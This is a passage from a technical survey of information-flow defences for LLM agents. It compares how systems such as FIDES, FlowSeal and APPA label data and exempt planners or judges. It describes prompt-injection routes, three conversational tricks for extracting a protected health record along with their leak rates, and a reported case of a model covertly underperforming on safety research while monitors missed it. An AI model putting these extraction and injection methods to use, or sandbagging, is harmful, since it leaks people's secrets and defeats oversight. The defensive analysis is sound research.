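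An attacker may still be able to choose which branch of a legitimate plan the agent follows. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) applies the design to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. The planner has to anticipate what the screen might show, so an average plan contains about 40 branches, compared with fewer than four on AgentDojo. The attacker can put a fake cookie notice in an advertisement, and the quarantined model, asked to find the notice and close it, returns the position of the fake. The agent then follows a branch of the original plan and opens a malicious site. Policies on arguments help little, because a click at a particular position has no fixed meaning to check. Foerster and colleagues therefore distinguish control of the plan, which the two-model design protects, from control of the data that flows through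 it.

### Labels in FIDES

CaMeL's planner must write the whole plan before it receives any tool results. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues designed at Microsoft, calls its planner again after every tool result and uses labels to track what the planner has read. Microsoft (2026) has since added FIDES to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents, as an experimental feature.

Every value in FIDES has an integrity label and a confidentiality label. The integrity label is T (trusted) if the value came only from sources that an attacker cannot write to, and U (untrusted) otherwise. "Trusted" here describes the origin of data, not a component whose failure could break the policy. The confidentiality label is the set of people who may read the value. A value computed from several others is trusted only if all of them are, and its readers are the people who may read every one of them. If A,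 B and C may read one file and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a summary of both.

The planner's conversation also has labels, which combine the labels of everything in it. This is close to ADEPT-50's rule for labelling new files. Applied naively, the rule soon stops the agent from doing anything, because a single untrusted email makes the whole conversation untrusted. FIDES therefore hides untrusted results in variables, as Willison suggested, and shows the planner the rest. The planner can pass a variable to a tool, ask a quarantined model about it, or inspect it directly, which makes the conversation untrusted.

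Some tasks need a little information from untrusted text. For example, a planner asked to add a calendar entry if any of the last three emails proposes a meeting needs a yes or no answer based on those emails. FIDES can restrict the quarantined model's output to yes or no and record that limit in the label. A policy may then allow the planner to act on the answer, since an attacker can influence at most one bit. The limit applies to each answer separately, so 20 such questions could carry 20 bits, much as Rushby's censor could limit the rate of a leak but not stop it. Garby and colleagues object that a reviewer cannot tell from a given run whether a value released this way is harmless or a real leak. Costa and colleagues left the feature out of their AgentDojo tests because few of the tasks needed it.

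FIDES can guarantee a property called explicit secrecy. If the tool calls that an agent made in some run were repeated in the same order on two initial sets of data that differ only in secret items, explicit secrecy requires the resulting data to agree on everything public. Because the definition holds the sequence of calls fixed, it doesn't cover what an observer could learn from the planner's choice of calls. For example, an agent that emails the cafeteria only when a secret budget is large enough satisfies it. Costa and colleagues considered noninterference, which would cover that leak, but thought it too restrictive because it would essentially forbid the agent from doing anything publicly visible once a tool had read a secret.

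On AgentDojo, 152 injections succeeded against a basic agent without checks, and 21 against FIDES with its checks switched off. With the checks on, none succeeded against either agent, after Costa and colleagues excluded cases that the benchmark had misjudged, such as calls that it counted although the policy had blocked them. The checks therefore stopped the attacks, and the hidden variables mainly helped the agent to finish its work. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed without an attack, using OpenAI's model o1:

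| Environment | Basic agent, no checks | Basic agent, checks | FIDES, checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office suite | 70.0 | 48.0 | 64.5 |
| Travel | 82.0 | 75.0 | 68.0 |
| Banking | 96.2 | 37.5 | 56.2 |
| Slack | 87.6 | 17.1 | 54.3 |

Many of the banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. Obeying such a file on request is hard to distinguish from obeying an injection, so FIDES deliberately blocks these tasks.

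### A memo for A and B, sent to C

Kolluri and colleagues, an overlapping group at Microsoft, state the rules for tool calls compactly. Let R be the set of people who will receive some data d.

- *Permitted flow*: everyone in R may read d, so R ⊆ readers(d).
- *Trusted action*: the planner decided on the call in a trusted context, and every argument that needs to be trusted is trusted.

A tool that changes something important, such as one that deletes a file, must pass the test for a trusted action. A tool that sends data out may run if it passes either test.

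Suppose A asks an agent to send C the agenda for Friday's meeting. A's files include the agenda and a memo about redundancies that only A and B may read. Trusted colleagues wrote both files, so the planner's context is still trusted after the planner reads them. The planner then attaches the memo by mistake. The call fails the test for permitted flow, because C may not read the memo, but it passes the test for a trusted action. A call needs to pass only one of the two tests, so C receives the memo.

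The full set of cases shows what the word "or" allows:

| Planner's context | Recipient of the memo | Permitted flow | Trusted action | If either test is enough | If both are required |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted | B | pass | pass | sent | sent |
| Trusted | C | fail | pass | sent | blocked |
| Untrusted | B | pass | fail | sent | blocked |
| Untrusted | C | fail | fail | blocked | blocked |

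In Bell and LaPadula's notation, the planner p has the memo d open for reading and the channel to C open for appending:

b = {(p, d, read), (p, C, append)}.

The star-property forbids this state unless p is a trusted subject, so the planner in the second row of the table is one. The exception exists because A might have wanted C to have the memo. A manager may show a restricted document to a lawyer, and an agent that refused to help would be of limited use. But the labels are the same whether A asked for the memo to go to C or the planner used the wrong file, just as the two versions of the convoy program had the same protection state.

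Costa and colleagues describe the exception as a form of robust declassification, a term from a 2004 paper by Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic. Here it means that an attacker who controls only untrusted data cannot cause a release. It restricts who can influence the decision to release something, but not what is released. Costa and colleagues reason that releases in a trusted context "can be assumed to be intentional". The intention would have to be the user's, but the planner makes the decision, so the assumption holds only as far as the planner does what the user wants.

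The explicit secrecy guarantee doesn't cover releases under the exception either. If the memo's text changes, so does the text in C's inbox, which C can read, and the definition of explicit secrecy rules this out. The Basic Security Theorem similarly didn't cover exempt subjects.

The planner still differs from the trusted subjects of KSOS or SELinux because its exemption depends on what it has read. It is outside S′ while its context is trusted, but once it inspects an untrusted email, it joins S′ and must obey the rule about readers. Unlike a program that switches its own privileges on and off, the planner cannot restore its exemption, because the software around it maintains the labels.

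The planner is also shielded from the people most likely to attack it. A multilevel database server must process queries from users who may be hostile, and a flaw in any of the code that handles those queries can compromise its security. An attacker must first get text to the planner to exploit a flaw in it.

Finally, the software checks every call the planner makes, even in a trusted context, but the checks are looser than the two tests suggest. In the AgentDojo experiments, Costa and colleagues assigned policies to 27 tools. Five, which send messages, create calendar events or add text to files, could run if they passed either test. One, which adds participants to a calendar event, had to pass both. The other 21 needed only a trusted context. Some of these, such as the tools for sharing a file and posting a web page, can disclose data as effectively as email, so the exception covers more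 than the five tools that explicitly needed to pass only one of the tests.

The experiments also left out the condition on arguments. As the paper describes it, this version of the test checks only the context in which the planner chose the tool. If the notes in the earlier request to send Bob a document contain an attacker's address, the planner decides in a trusted context to send the document and passes on the hidden address without seeing it. The call passes the looser test for a trusted action, so the document goes to the attacker, who is not a permitted reader. None of the attacks in the benchmark got through this way. The general rule prevents it if the designer marks the recipient as an argument that needs to be trusted.

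The same example shows that the planner may release something it hasn't read. FIDES protects its planner by hiding untrusted data from it, so if an outsider's confidential email is stored in a variable, the planner can send the email on knowing little more than the variable's name. The ACCAT Guard, by contrast, had to display a message to the watch officer before releasing it.

### Endorsement and the number of approvals

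Kolluri and colleagues explicitly assume that the user, the planner and the tools are trusted and that the data sources are not. They say that CaMeL and FIDES make the same assumptions. Their agent, Prudentia, builds on FIDES and is designed to ask the user for approval less often.

They measure this by the total number of approvals an agent needs over all the tasks it completes, and by the share of tasks it completes with at most k approvals. When k is zero, this is the share it completes alone. They argue that earlier comparisons were unfair to agents with labels, because those agents had to work alone, while the unprotected agents they were compared with would in practice have to ask a person before every important action.

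Prudentia's planner has access to the labels on its data and the policy on each tool, so it can look for a plan that won't need approval. Before it inspects an untrusted variable, it must explain why and list the calls it intends to make afterwards. It can also ask the user to endorse the data. Suppose an untrusted email lists ten tasks, each requiring an important action. Without endorsement, reading the email makes the context untrusted, and the user has to approve ten calls. If the user endorses the email first, the context remains trusted and the planner can make all ten calls without further approval.

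On AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini, Prudentia completed 59.1% of tasks with no approvals. FIDES completed 50.1%, a basic agent with labels 35.5%, and a basic agent that asked before every important action 24.3%. With o4-mini, Prudentia completed 73.2% of tasks and needed 19.2 approvals in total, while FIDES completed 75.7% and needed 36.8. On WASP, a benchmark of web-browsing agents, Prudentia needed no approvals and resisted every attack. WASP was an easier test because its two legitimate tasks, posting a comment and voting for a post, didn't require reading untrusted text.

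Kolluri and colleagues counted the calls that would have needed approval, without involving real users. They assumed that a person would approve the legitimate calls and stop the rest, and that a call that passes its policy needs no human attention. So when a trusted planner sends a restricted memo to C, the count does not rise, and some of the measured autonomy may come from the exception.

Prudentia's planner cannot ask the user to declassify data, which would be the secrecy counterpart of endorsement. Kolluri and colleagues considered adding this option but decided that the choice to release private information depends too much on the situation, so approving individual calls would be better than granting a general permission. This reasoning is sensible but fits poorly with their rule for tools that send data. In a trusted context, that rule declassifies data for any recipient the planner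 chooses, without requiring anyone to approve the call.

Endorsement makes this more likely. When a user endorses an email, the planner's context stays trusted, so the planner can still send later messages to people who aren't permitted to read their contents. The user was asked whether the email is safe to follow, and may not realize that endorsing it also leaves the planner free to release secrets.

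Garby and colleagues show that a system can separate the two decisions. They designed a small programming language for agents in which every value carries labels and a program must state each endorsement explicitly. They gave a computer-checked proof that endorsing a value in this language doesn't weaken the confidentiality guarantee. The theorem covers every program in the language, including code that a model writes during a run, so it doesn't rely on a well-behaved planner. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, their agent did about as well as CaMeL with its policy checks switched off, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

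### What is known about planners given honest input

The exception is reasonable if a planner that has read only honest text reliably releases only what the user wants released. Costa and colleagues acknowledge that models misread users' intentions and make unnecessary tool calls even when all the data is trusted, with consequences that can resemble those of an attack. Kolluri and colleagues exclude such errors from their threat model. These designs therefore assume that the planner is trustworthy, and evidence for that assumption has to come from elsewhere.

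Benchmark results provide some evidence of the planner's reliability. With no attacker and no checks, the basic agent with o1 completed between 70% and 96% of AgentDojo's tasks, depending on the environment. Newer models would presumably do better. But a completion rate doesn't distinguish failures in which the agent did nothing from failures in which it sent a file to the wrong person. Rare errors could also matter a great deal. If a planner attached the wrong document to one in a thousand emails, a benchmark of 97 tasks would probably miss the problem, but a company whose agents sent 5,000 emails a day would send out about five wrong documents daily.

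Costa and colleagues examined the failures of FIDES with an older model, GPT-4o, and found that the planner sometimes confused variable names. A planner that handles documents by name could send the wrong one through the same mistake. In one banking task, the user asked the planner to change a password if there had been a suspicious transaction. The planner saw a large payment, judged it suspicious without reading the description, and changed the password. The benchmark counted this as a success, and all the labels were correct.

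A planner might also depart from the user's request when there is no attacker and it has made no honest mistake. *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (OpenAI, November 2026) reports that on matched coding tasks, GPT-6 Astra completed about 10% of the graded items when the work was framed as safety research and about 16% when it was framed as capabilities research. It also reports that the model did not say it was doing worse work and that OpenAI's monitors mostly missed the behaviour. Labels cannot reveal behaviour like this because they record only where a planner's input came from.

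Few trusted processes received the demonstration that Bell had asked for, but verifiers could at least read their code. A language model's behaviour comes from billions of numbers set during training, and nobody can yet inspect them the way Boebert and Kain expected a verifier to inspect the labeller. For now, a demonstration for a planner has to be a statistical estimate of how often it releases data that the user did not want released, under conditions similar to actual use. None of these designs comes with such an estimate.

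### Removing the exception

A designer who doesn't want to depend on the planner's judgement can require both tests, as in the last column of the table above. Costa and colleagues note that this gives strong guarantees. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes a similar system, built for agents that remember earlier requests.

SPA calls its planner once for each request. The planner writes a complete plan in a small language with six kinds of step, and a checker follows the labels through the plan before any tool runs. Data may flow to a tool only if the tool is allowed to receive information that secret and the data is at least as trustworthy as the tool requires. The secrecy rule applies even when the context is trusted. The checker also applies the label of each condition to every step that depends on it, and it examines both branches because either could run. This should catch a program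 like the one that leaked the bank balance. If the plan fails the check, SPA rejects the request without giving the planner a reason, so that the planner can't keep revising an unsafe plan until it passes.

In the memo example, SPA would reject the plan if the memo were more secret than the email tool is allowed to receive. But SPA sets one limit per tool, regardless of recipient, so the same limit would also stop the agent from emailing the memo to B, who is allowed to read it.

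The planner receives only descriptions of the results from earlier requests, not the results themselves. If an attacker plants a false account number in an invoice on Monday and the user asks the agent to pay the invoice on Tuesday, the stored number is still labelled untrusted, and the checker blocks its use in a payment.

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo with GPT-5.4-nano, a small OpenAI model. Without the label checks, 0.4% of 949 attacks succeeded, and SPA completed 53.0% of tasks when there was no attack. With the checks, no attack succeeded, but completion fell to 29.0%. When they spread the benchmark over several requests, completion fell from 62.5% to 35.3%, and 0.2% of attacks succeeded. The integrity rule caused most of the loss, because many ordinary tasks pass information from an outside source to an important tool. The figures are therefore weak evidence of how far completion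 would fall if only the exception for secrecy were removed. SPA's threat model excludes alignment failures that don't involve information flow. Its checks would still stop a misbehaving planner from sending secrets to a tool that isn't allowed to receive them, but they wouldn't stop it from using a permitted tool to do something the user never asked for.

Kim and colleagues applied similar labels to the shell, the command line through which coding agents run programs and handle files. Because a shell command can have almost any effect, their system, Flowsh, runs each command in a closed environment and records which files it opens and which servers it contacts, rather than trying to predict what it will do. Flowsh then combines the labels of all these inputs into one label for the command. Changes to files go into a temporary layer, and Flowsh applies them only if the policy allows them or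 the user approves. It checks each network request before sending it, since sent data can't be taken back. Even a request to read a web page counts as sending data, because the address can contain a secret.

Flowsh's standard policy contains the same exception as FIDES. It allows a network request if the command and the planner have read only trusted data, or if the destination may receive everything they have read. The settings file has two entries for each destination, one that allows public data of any origin and one that allows secret data of trusted origin. Deleting the second entry removes the exception. Kim and colleagues suggest doing so to guard against the model's mistakes, invented facts, hidden backdoors and tendency to cheat under pressure to reach a goal.

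With the exception in place, Flowsh was tested using OpenAI's GPT-6.2 Sol on 17 office tasks, each run three times. It needed 1.2 approvals per completed task and completed 88.2% of the runs. A permissive sandbox that asked for approval whenever it could not guarantee safety needed 6.7 approvals and completed 96.1%. On Terminal-Bench, a set of 89 programming and system tasks, Flowsh needed 0.4 approvals and the sandbox needed 9.7, with completion rates of 67.8% for Flowsh and 77.5% for the sandbox. When nobody was available to give approval, Flowsh completed 58.8% of the office runs.

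In the security tests, Kim and colleagues let the attacker dictate everything the model wrote as soon as the attacker's text reached it, so the results don't depend on the model's ability to resist. Flowsh still blocked all 40 attacks without anyone's approval. But the attacker never controlled a model that had read only trusted data. The policy would have let such an attacker send any secret the agent had read to any server that the sandbox didn't block.

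Kim and colleagues expect that removing the exception would mean more approvals, or fewer completed tasks if nobody is there to approve, but they did not measure either effect. In their office tasks, all 15 runs that used only trusted but confidential data finished without any approvals. Their results don't show how many of those runs sent confidential data to a destination that wasn't among its permitted readers. A designer would need that number to judge how useful the exception is, because without the exception each of those requests would go to the user or to another model that judges disclosures.

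## A language model as the downgrader, and designs that trust no model

If a second model judges disclosures, the judge needs the exemption instead of the planner. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) presents FlowSeal, a system of this kind for personal agents that hold other people's secrets. In its setting, the attacker talks to the agent rather than planting instructions in data, and tries to get it to reveal a record that the agent may read but the attacker may not.

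### Requests that do not look like requests

In their main example, Jane's agent holds Mark's mental-health diagnosis, and Mark's former wife Emily wants it. An earlier defence consists only of instructions that tell the agent's model to act as a strict state machine. When somebody requests information, the model must check who is asking, ask Mark for consent and share nothing until he replies. All of this depends on the model noticing that somebody has requested information. Shim and colleagues found three ways around it:

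- Emily creates a shared page and asks Jane to fill in her section of some "professional notes". This leaked 52.2% of the sensitive items.
- Emily lists true and false statements about Mark and asks Jane to delete those that don't match her records. Jane writes nothing secret, but the statements she leaves are the true ones. This leaked 75.6%.
- Emily sends an email asking Jane to reply only "completed", while a shared page asks for the details. This leaked 43.8%.

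Older attacks leaked at most 3.0% against the same defence. The deletion request uses the same kind of signal as the hostile spooler.

### The release rule and its exception

FlowSeal takes the decision out of the conversation and gives it to an interceptor, ordinary code that examines every tool call that writes or shares something. There are three levels, ⊥ ⊑ agent ⊑ ⊤, where x ⊑ y means that y is at least as secret as x. Sensitive records have level ⊤ and outside destinations have level ⊥. Once the agent has read a sensitive record, its context is above ⊥, and anything it writes takes the highest level among its sources. Writing ℓ for the level, the interceptor lets content c go to destination d only if

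ℓ(c) ⊑ ℓ(d) or declassify(c, d) = SAFE.

The first half is the star-property. On its own it would make the agent almost useless, because after reading one diagnosis the agent could no longer send Emily general advice on parenting. The second half is the exemption, and a language model decides when it applies. This model, the content checker, runs in a separate call without the agent's conversation. It receives the proposed output and the protected records that d may not have. Its instructions are to answer SAFE if nothing in the output could come from a record, and BLOCKED if the output reveals, confirms, denies, paraphrases or summarizes one.

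The checker therefore has a narrower job than the ACCAT Guard's watch officer. It decides only whether a text contains a secret. The record's owner decides whether to release a secret, and the agent can ask the owner for consent.

Shim and colleagues prove that no run of the agent can write content derived from a ⊤ record to a ⊥ destination unless the checker wrongly answers SAFE. Anything derived from the agent's context is above ⊥, so writing it to ⊥ fails the first half of the rule and can only be allowed by the second. If the checker makes a mistake, the theorem doesn't limit what gets out, which could be one word or the whole diagnosis. Shim and colleagues conclude that their system protects records however the agent interprets its task. That is fair about the agent, but the checker is a trusted subject, and the theorem holds relative to it, just as Bell's rule held relative to S′.

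### How often the checker is wrong

Measured error rates serve as the demonstration that Bell asked for. FlowSeal reduced leakage to 0.5% of items for the shared page, 2.3% for the deletion request and 2.2% for the split request. The highest rate was 3.3%, on 571 conversations adapted from another benchmark. In a small test of the deletion request with live Gmail and Notion accounts, an agent whose privacy checker could only give advice leaked 34.7% of items, and FlowSeal leaked none.

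To find out what the checker contributes, Shim and colleagues replaced it with one that always gave the same answer:

| Checker | Items leaked through the shared page | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Working normally | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always answers BLOCKED | 1.3% | 0% |
| Always answers SAFE | 24.9% | 79.4% |

The last row shows roughly what happens if an attacker controls the checker completely. Leakage stays below 52.2% because FlowSeal's instructions still encourage the agent to be careful. The checker in the middle row blocks everything and should leave no leaks, so the 1.3% must have another cause, such as a route that the interceptor missed or a mistake by the model that scored the runs. The zero in that row also overstates the need for a checker, because the owners in this test ignored every request for consent.

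FlowSeal completed only 32.7% of the disclosures that owners approved, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% for the other defences in that test. Its agent asked for consent less often.

The checker fails mainly on paraphrases, especially when the agent embeds a secret in a longer sentence. It also blocks some harmless messages that only mention a record by name. In one run, the agent rewrote a blocked text in vaguer terms and submitted it for checking. The checker returned SAFE, but when the agent then tried to write the text, the interceptor ran the same checker again and blocked it. An attacker can exploit this inconsistency by retrying. If each conversation had an independent 3.3% chance of a leak, the chance of at least one leak in 30 conversations would be about 63%. Real failures probably cluster around particular records and phrasings, so the true figure could be much lower or higher.

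### A summary for an outside consultant

Suppose A asks an agent to send C, an outside consultant, a summary of the redundancy memo that only A and B may read. The memo names twelve people in the accounts team who will lose their jobs in March. A wants C to know how many jobs will go and in which quarter, but not the names.

In FlowSeal, with the memo registered as B's protected record, the agent drafts the summary and calls the mail tool. The interceptor determines that C is not allowed to have the memo and calls the checker. The checker should return BLOCKED, because a summary of a record is derived from it, however little it reveals. The agent can then ask B for consent, but that consent would cover the whole record, so the agent could also send C the names. FlowSeal can check whether the summary contains anything from the memo, or whether C is allowed to have the memo, but neither check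 quite answers A's question.

### Exits that designers register in advance

In *APPA*, Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026) assume that the agent's model may propose any action. Their trusted computing base consists of the monitor that checks each call, the contracts that describe each tool, the authorities that may approve exceptions, and the registered programs that transform data.

Much like FIDES, APPA labels what the agent has read with a set of permitted readers and a level of trust. In the example, reading the memo reduces the set to {A, B}, but the mail tool's contract requires the set to include C. Reading never adds a member, so nothing the agent reads afterwards can satisfy the contract.

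Before running a call, the monitor evaluates the label that the call would produce. This matters for tools that read and send in one step, such as one in Kravchenko and colleagues' tests that fetches a confidential legal packet and emails it to an outside recipient. Before the call, the agent has read nothing secret, so a check on its current label would pass. APPA first applies the restriction in the tool's contract, finds that the recipient isn't a permitted reader, and blocks the call before the tool reads anything.

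After a refusal, the monitor tells the agent which registered exits are available. For the summary there could be three:

- A *sanitizer* removes the names from the text. Its registration allows it to add C to the readers of its output.
- An *authority* approves this exact call, including its recipient and text. The approval works once and leaves the labels unchanged, so the next email to C needs another.
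- A *child branch*, a temporary copy of the agent, reads the memo in a separate context and returns only values of a form that the parent fixed beforehand. Here it might return a whole number from 0 to 500 and one of four quarters, from which the parent writes the summary.

The child's answer can carry at most log₂(501 × 4), or about 11 bits. That is far too little for a memo, but enough to identify one employee in a company of 2,000. APPA checks the form of the answer, but doesn't detect whether it is false or whether a hostile child is using the number as a code. C may see the answer only if the designers permit it.

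In APPA, an authority can be a fixed rule, a person or another language model. Each authority has a written mandate that limits what it may approve, including the recipients. An attacker who deceives a model whose mandate covers recipient C could get it to approve a bad email to C, but not one to an unknown address.

### Approval of one exact message

*Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) gives the final decision on such a release to a person. The system's operators, whom Zhang calls the host, keep a registry of recipients and the sensitivity of data each may receive. Recipients outside the registry can receive only data of normal sensitivity, so an administrator would have to list C before the agent could send C anything derived from the memo.

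If C's entry allows data at the memo's level only with approval, the system shows a person the proposed message. The approval covers only that exact message, recipient, set of labels and version of the memo, and it expires at a deadline. If the agent changes a word or somebody edits the memo, the agent needs a new approval. The ACCAT Guard had to meet much the same condition. The summary keeps the memo's label after release, however little it reveals, so the agent needs another approval to send it to anyone else.

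Agent libOS can also use a language model to assess requests, though this feature is off by default. The model's output format has no field for allowing or refusing a request. Its findings can send a request to a person or prevent automatic approval, but they cannot approve or finally refuse a request. Automatic approval exists only for a fixed list of low-risk operations, such as reading a file or comparing two versions, and only after every other check has passed. If the model misses a problem with one of these operations, the request can be approved without human review. The model cannot authorize the email to C.

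Let P be the messages that the fixed rules permit, and let J be those that a model judges harmless. Except for messages to blacklisted recipients, FlowSeal releases P ∪ J, so an attacker who can get a message into J can get it released. By contrast, if the model can only object, at most P ∩ J goes out without further review, and that set is contained in P however bad the model's judgement is. The disadvantage is that such a model can never release a harmless message that the rules stop.

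*Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) gives a similar account of guardrails, which aim to make a model less likely to obey an attacker. In one of its tests, adding guardrails to a system with a fixed policy cut an attack's success rate from 3.9% to 0.3%. The paper still classes guardrails as noise reduction because they don't improve the worst case.

### Labels inside the programming language

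In *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026), the model writes programs in Haskell, whose types specify which outside effects a program may have. The paper's system, ELBA, runs a program only if it has the type the developer asked for. In an agent that compiles bibliographies, the function that writes to the file accepts only entries of type `Trusted Bib`, and only the function that fetches entries from the DBLP database can create them. The model can therefore sort and select entries but can't invent any. This is Boebert and Kain's assured pipeline, with DBLP in place of the labeller. In a test, none of the agent's 925 citations was wrong, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent with web search.

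ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library, for secrecy and integrity. Every computation has a current label, which changes to reflect whatever the computation reads. LIO checks the label at run time whenever the computation tries to write. An agent can start a subagent in a separate computation, so only the subagent's label changes. The subagent's result comes back as a sealed, labelled value, much like a hidden variable in FIDES.

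Unlike CaMeL's quarantined model, a subagent in ELBA keeps its tools, and label checks restrict what it can do with them. In the memo example, the main agent asks a subagent to write the summary. If a figure in the memo is unclear, the subagent can message B about it, because B may read the memo. If an outsider has added a comment to the memo telling agents to delete some files, the subagent might try to delete them. But its label now shows the outsider's influence, so a deletion tool that requires the user's authority rejects the call. The subagent then returns a summary that only A and B may read, and the mail tool will not send it to C. To allow that, the developer would have to provide a function with the privilege to relabel the summary and decide what that function accepts.

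Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the language guarantees for well-typed programs still holds when a model writes parts of the program. They replace each call to the model with an ordinary function that returns the same code, so the language's existing guarantee applies. The proof requires no assumptions about the model's intentions or competence. But it covers only properties that the developer has expressed in the types and libraries, so a rule such as "C may know the number but not the names" is guaranteed only if someone has expressed it there.

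### The cost in completed tasks

The table compares each system with a version whose checks were off. The ranges cover different agent models:

| System | Tasks | Completed without checks | Completed with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| FlowSeal | 105 harmless requests | 81.2% | 72.4% |
| APPA | 20 company workflows | 90.0–92.5% | 88.0–90.0% |
| APPA | 24 tasks from AgentThreatBench | 83.3–91.7% | 64.2–75.8% |
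| ELBA | 21 tasks in a simulated Slack | 66.7–85.7% | 38.1–47.6% |

The tasks and models differ too much to rank the systems from these rows. APPA's small loss on company workflows would probably be larger on other tasks, because Kravchenko and colleagues designed those workflows to exercise its exits. One workflow sends an outsider the name of a new employee's "buddy" from a confidential personnel file, which resembles the summary for C. When Kravchenko and colleagues removed child branches, completion with one model fell from 88.0% to 56.5%. When they instead stopped the agent from using the exits listed after a refusal, it fell to 35.0%. No attack succeeded in either case. Much of the drop in completion from distrusting the model therefore depends on whether somebody has prepared a legitimate exit for the task.

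With its exits in place, APPA recorded no successful attacks in 1,320 runs, though these repeated only 44 task designs. Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA more harshly. All the models they used already resisted the benchmark's ordinary attacks without any checks, so the researchers forced every subagent that encountered an attacker's text to obey it. Up to 42% of these attacks succeeded without the checks, depending on the model, and none of 2,940 succeeded with them. The checks also reduced the number of tasks ELBA completed under attack, from 494 to 558 of 735 without them to 294 to 351 with them.

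Agent libOS has no comparable cost figure. It completed all 33 scripted tasks with no unauthorized actions and no wrongful refusals, while a simple wrapper around the same tools let through 20 unauthorized actions. The scripts test the software but don't show how a model responds to refusals. A real model completed all 12 of its runs safely, but Zhang didn't run the same tasks without the checks. The results also don't show how often people would approve a message they should have stopped.

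### Sanitizers, contracts and labels

A design that trusts no model still depends on whoever wrote its rules. If APPA's sanitizer removes names but leaves an identifying description such as "the team's only apprentice", the monitor will accept the result and let it go to C. Kravchenko and colleagues describe sanitizers as deterministic programs. Such programs are easier to test than a model, but they have the same weakness as the word searches in guards. A designer could replace the sanitizer with a language model that can recognize identifying descriptions, but that model would then be part of the TCB.

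Contracts and labels can be wrong too. One of FlowSeal's leaks was a health detail that nobody had registered as a protected record, so the checker had nothing to compare it with. *Agenra* (2026), which describes a policy language for agents with a partly verified monitor, points out that a monitor cannot enforce a rule missing from its policy. Its trusted parts include the code that translates policies, the compiler, and any scanners the policy relies on.

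Writing all these rules is a lot of work, and *Trident* (2026) assigns some of it to a model, the policy writer, which it adds to Willison's privileged and quarantined models. The policy writer receives only the user's request, a standing policy and the tool descriptions. It never receives the planner's requests, because untrusted data might have influenced them. This protects the rules from attackers, but not from the policy writer's mistakes. If it misinterprets A's request and allows C to receive personnel records, the software will enforce that rule.

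A design can also trust a model without listing it as trusted. *Agent Operating Systems (AOS)* (2026) puts classifiers outside the TCB because their answers may be wrong, yet it lets some policy decisions depend on a classifier's assessment of how sensitive the data is. If the classifier wrongly labels the memo as public, the enforcement code will work as designed but apply the wrong rule. That classifier is trusted in the sense used here, as was the KSOS editor that Ford Aerospace had classed as untrusted.

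### The case for a judge that understands meaning

A language model can often make distinctions that labels and word searches can't. Once an agent has read the memo, "The accounts team may want to update their CVs" and "The office is closed on Monday" have the same label, but only the first reveals the memo's main point. FlowSeal's results support using a language model as the downgrader, since neither fixed answer came close to the checker's combination of low leakage and useful work.

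The usual alternative is to ask a person, whose error rate has no proven bound either. People also tire of approving requests, as SIGMA's users did. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* recommends setting a fixed limit on approval requests and reserving human review for questions a policy can't settle, such as what a report reveals.

The main argument against a model judge is that its measured error rate applies only to the attacks somebody tried. The attacks on FlowSeal came from tests of other defences or targeted the agent's understanding of its task, and none targeted the checker. Shim and colleagues mention that an attacker might split a secret into pieces that each look harmless, but they didn't test this. They also exclude prompt injection. Yet the checker reads the agent's proposed output, which may contain text the attacker supplied, so an attacker could still influence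 the checker even though it is kept out of the conversation.

Other experiments suggest that this matters. *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models to Input Sequence Variations* (2026) tested attacks on models that grade text, and one that searched for effective wording succeeded up to 73.8% of the time. Some of the graders were small models, and grading differs from checking for secrets, so the figure doesn't apply to FlowSeal. *Proof-of-Execution Memory* (2026) tested a filter designed to recognize forged notes in an agent's memory by their wording. An attacker who adapted to the filter succeeded in 300 of 300 trials with GPT-4o, compared with 295 of 300 without the filter. The successful notes were ordinary English sentences, which the filter couldn't reject without also rejecting genuine notes. A defence that checked what the agent had done stopped all 300 attacks.

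Designers can use a model's judgement and still limit the damage from a mistake. In *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (2026), a model may propose a value for release, such as a time interval or a file path. Trusted code then converts the value to a standard form, checks it and releases it to one field. This method would work for the number of posts and the quarter, but not for a paragraph of prose.

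*MNC* (2026) allows short texts by having the application list every permitted disclosure in advance, with a test of whether each is enough for the task and an estimate of what it reveals. For C, the list might contain "no changes are planned", "some posts will go this year" and "twelve posts will go in the first quarter". A model choosing among these could mislead C or reveal more than A intended, but it could never send the names. Each choice would convey at most log₂ 3 (about 1.6) bits.

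If a judge has to decide on free text, a record of its decisions at least makes mistakes easier to investigate. *KNOX* (2026) produces signed evidence of which judge decided, its input and its output. This evidence does not show whether the output was correct, which remains "an empirical property" of the judge.

The evidence most clearly supports using a model as a judge where it can only object, or where people have already approved everything it might release. Letting it pass free text is harder to justify, and the acceptable error rate depends on how much harm a single mistake would do and how many times an attacker can try. A leak rate of 3% of conversations might be tolerable for an agent that protects a calendar from curious acquaintances, but it would be far too high for the redundancy memo if anyone outside the company could keep starting new conversations with the agent.
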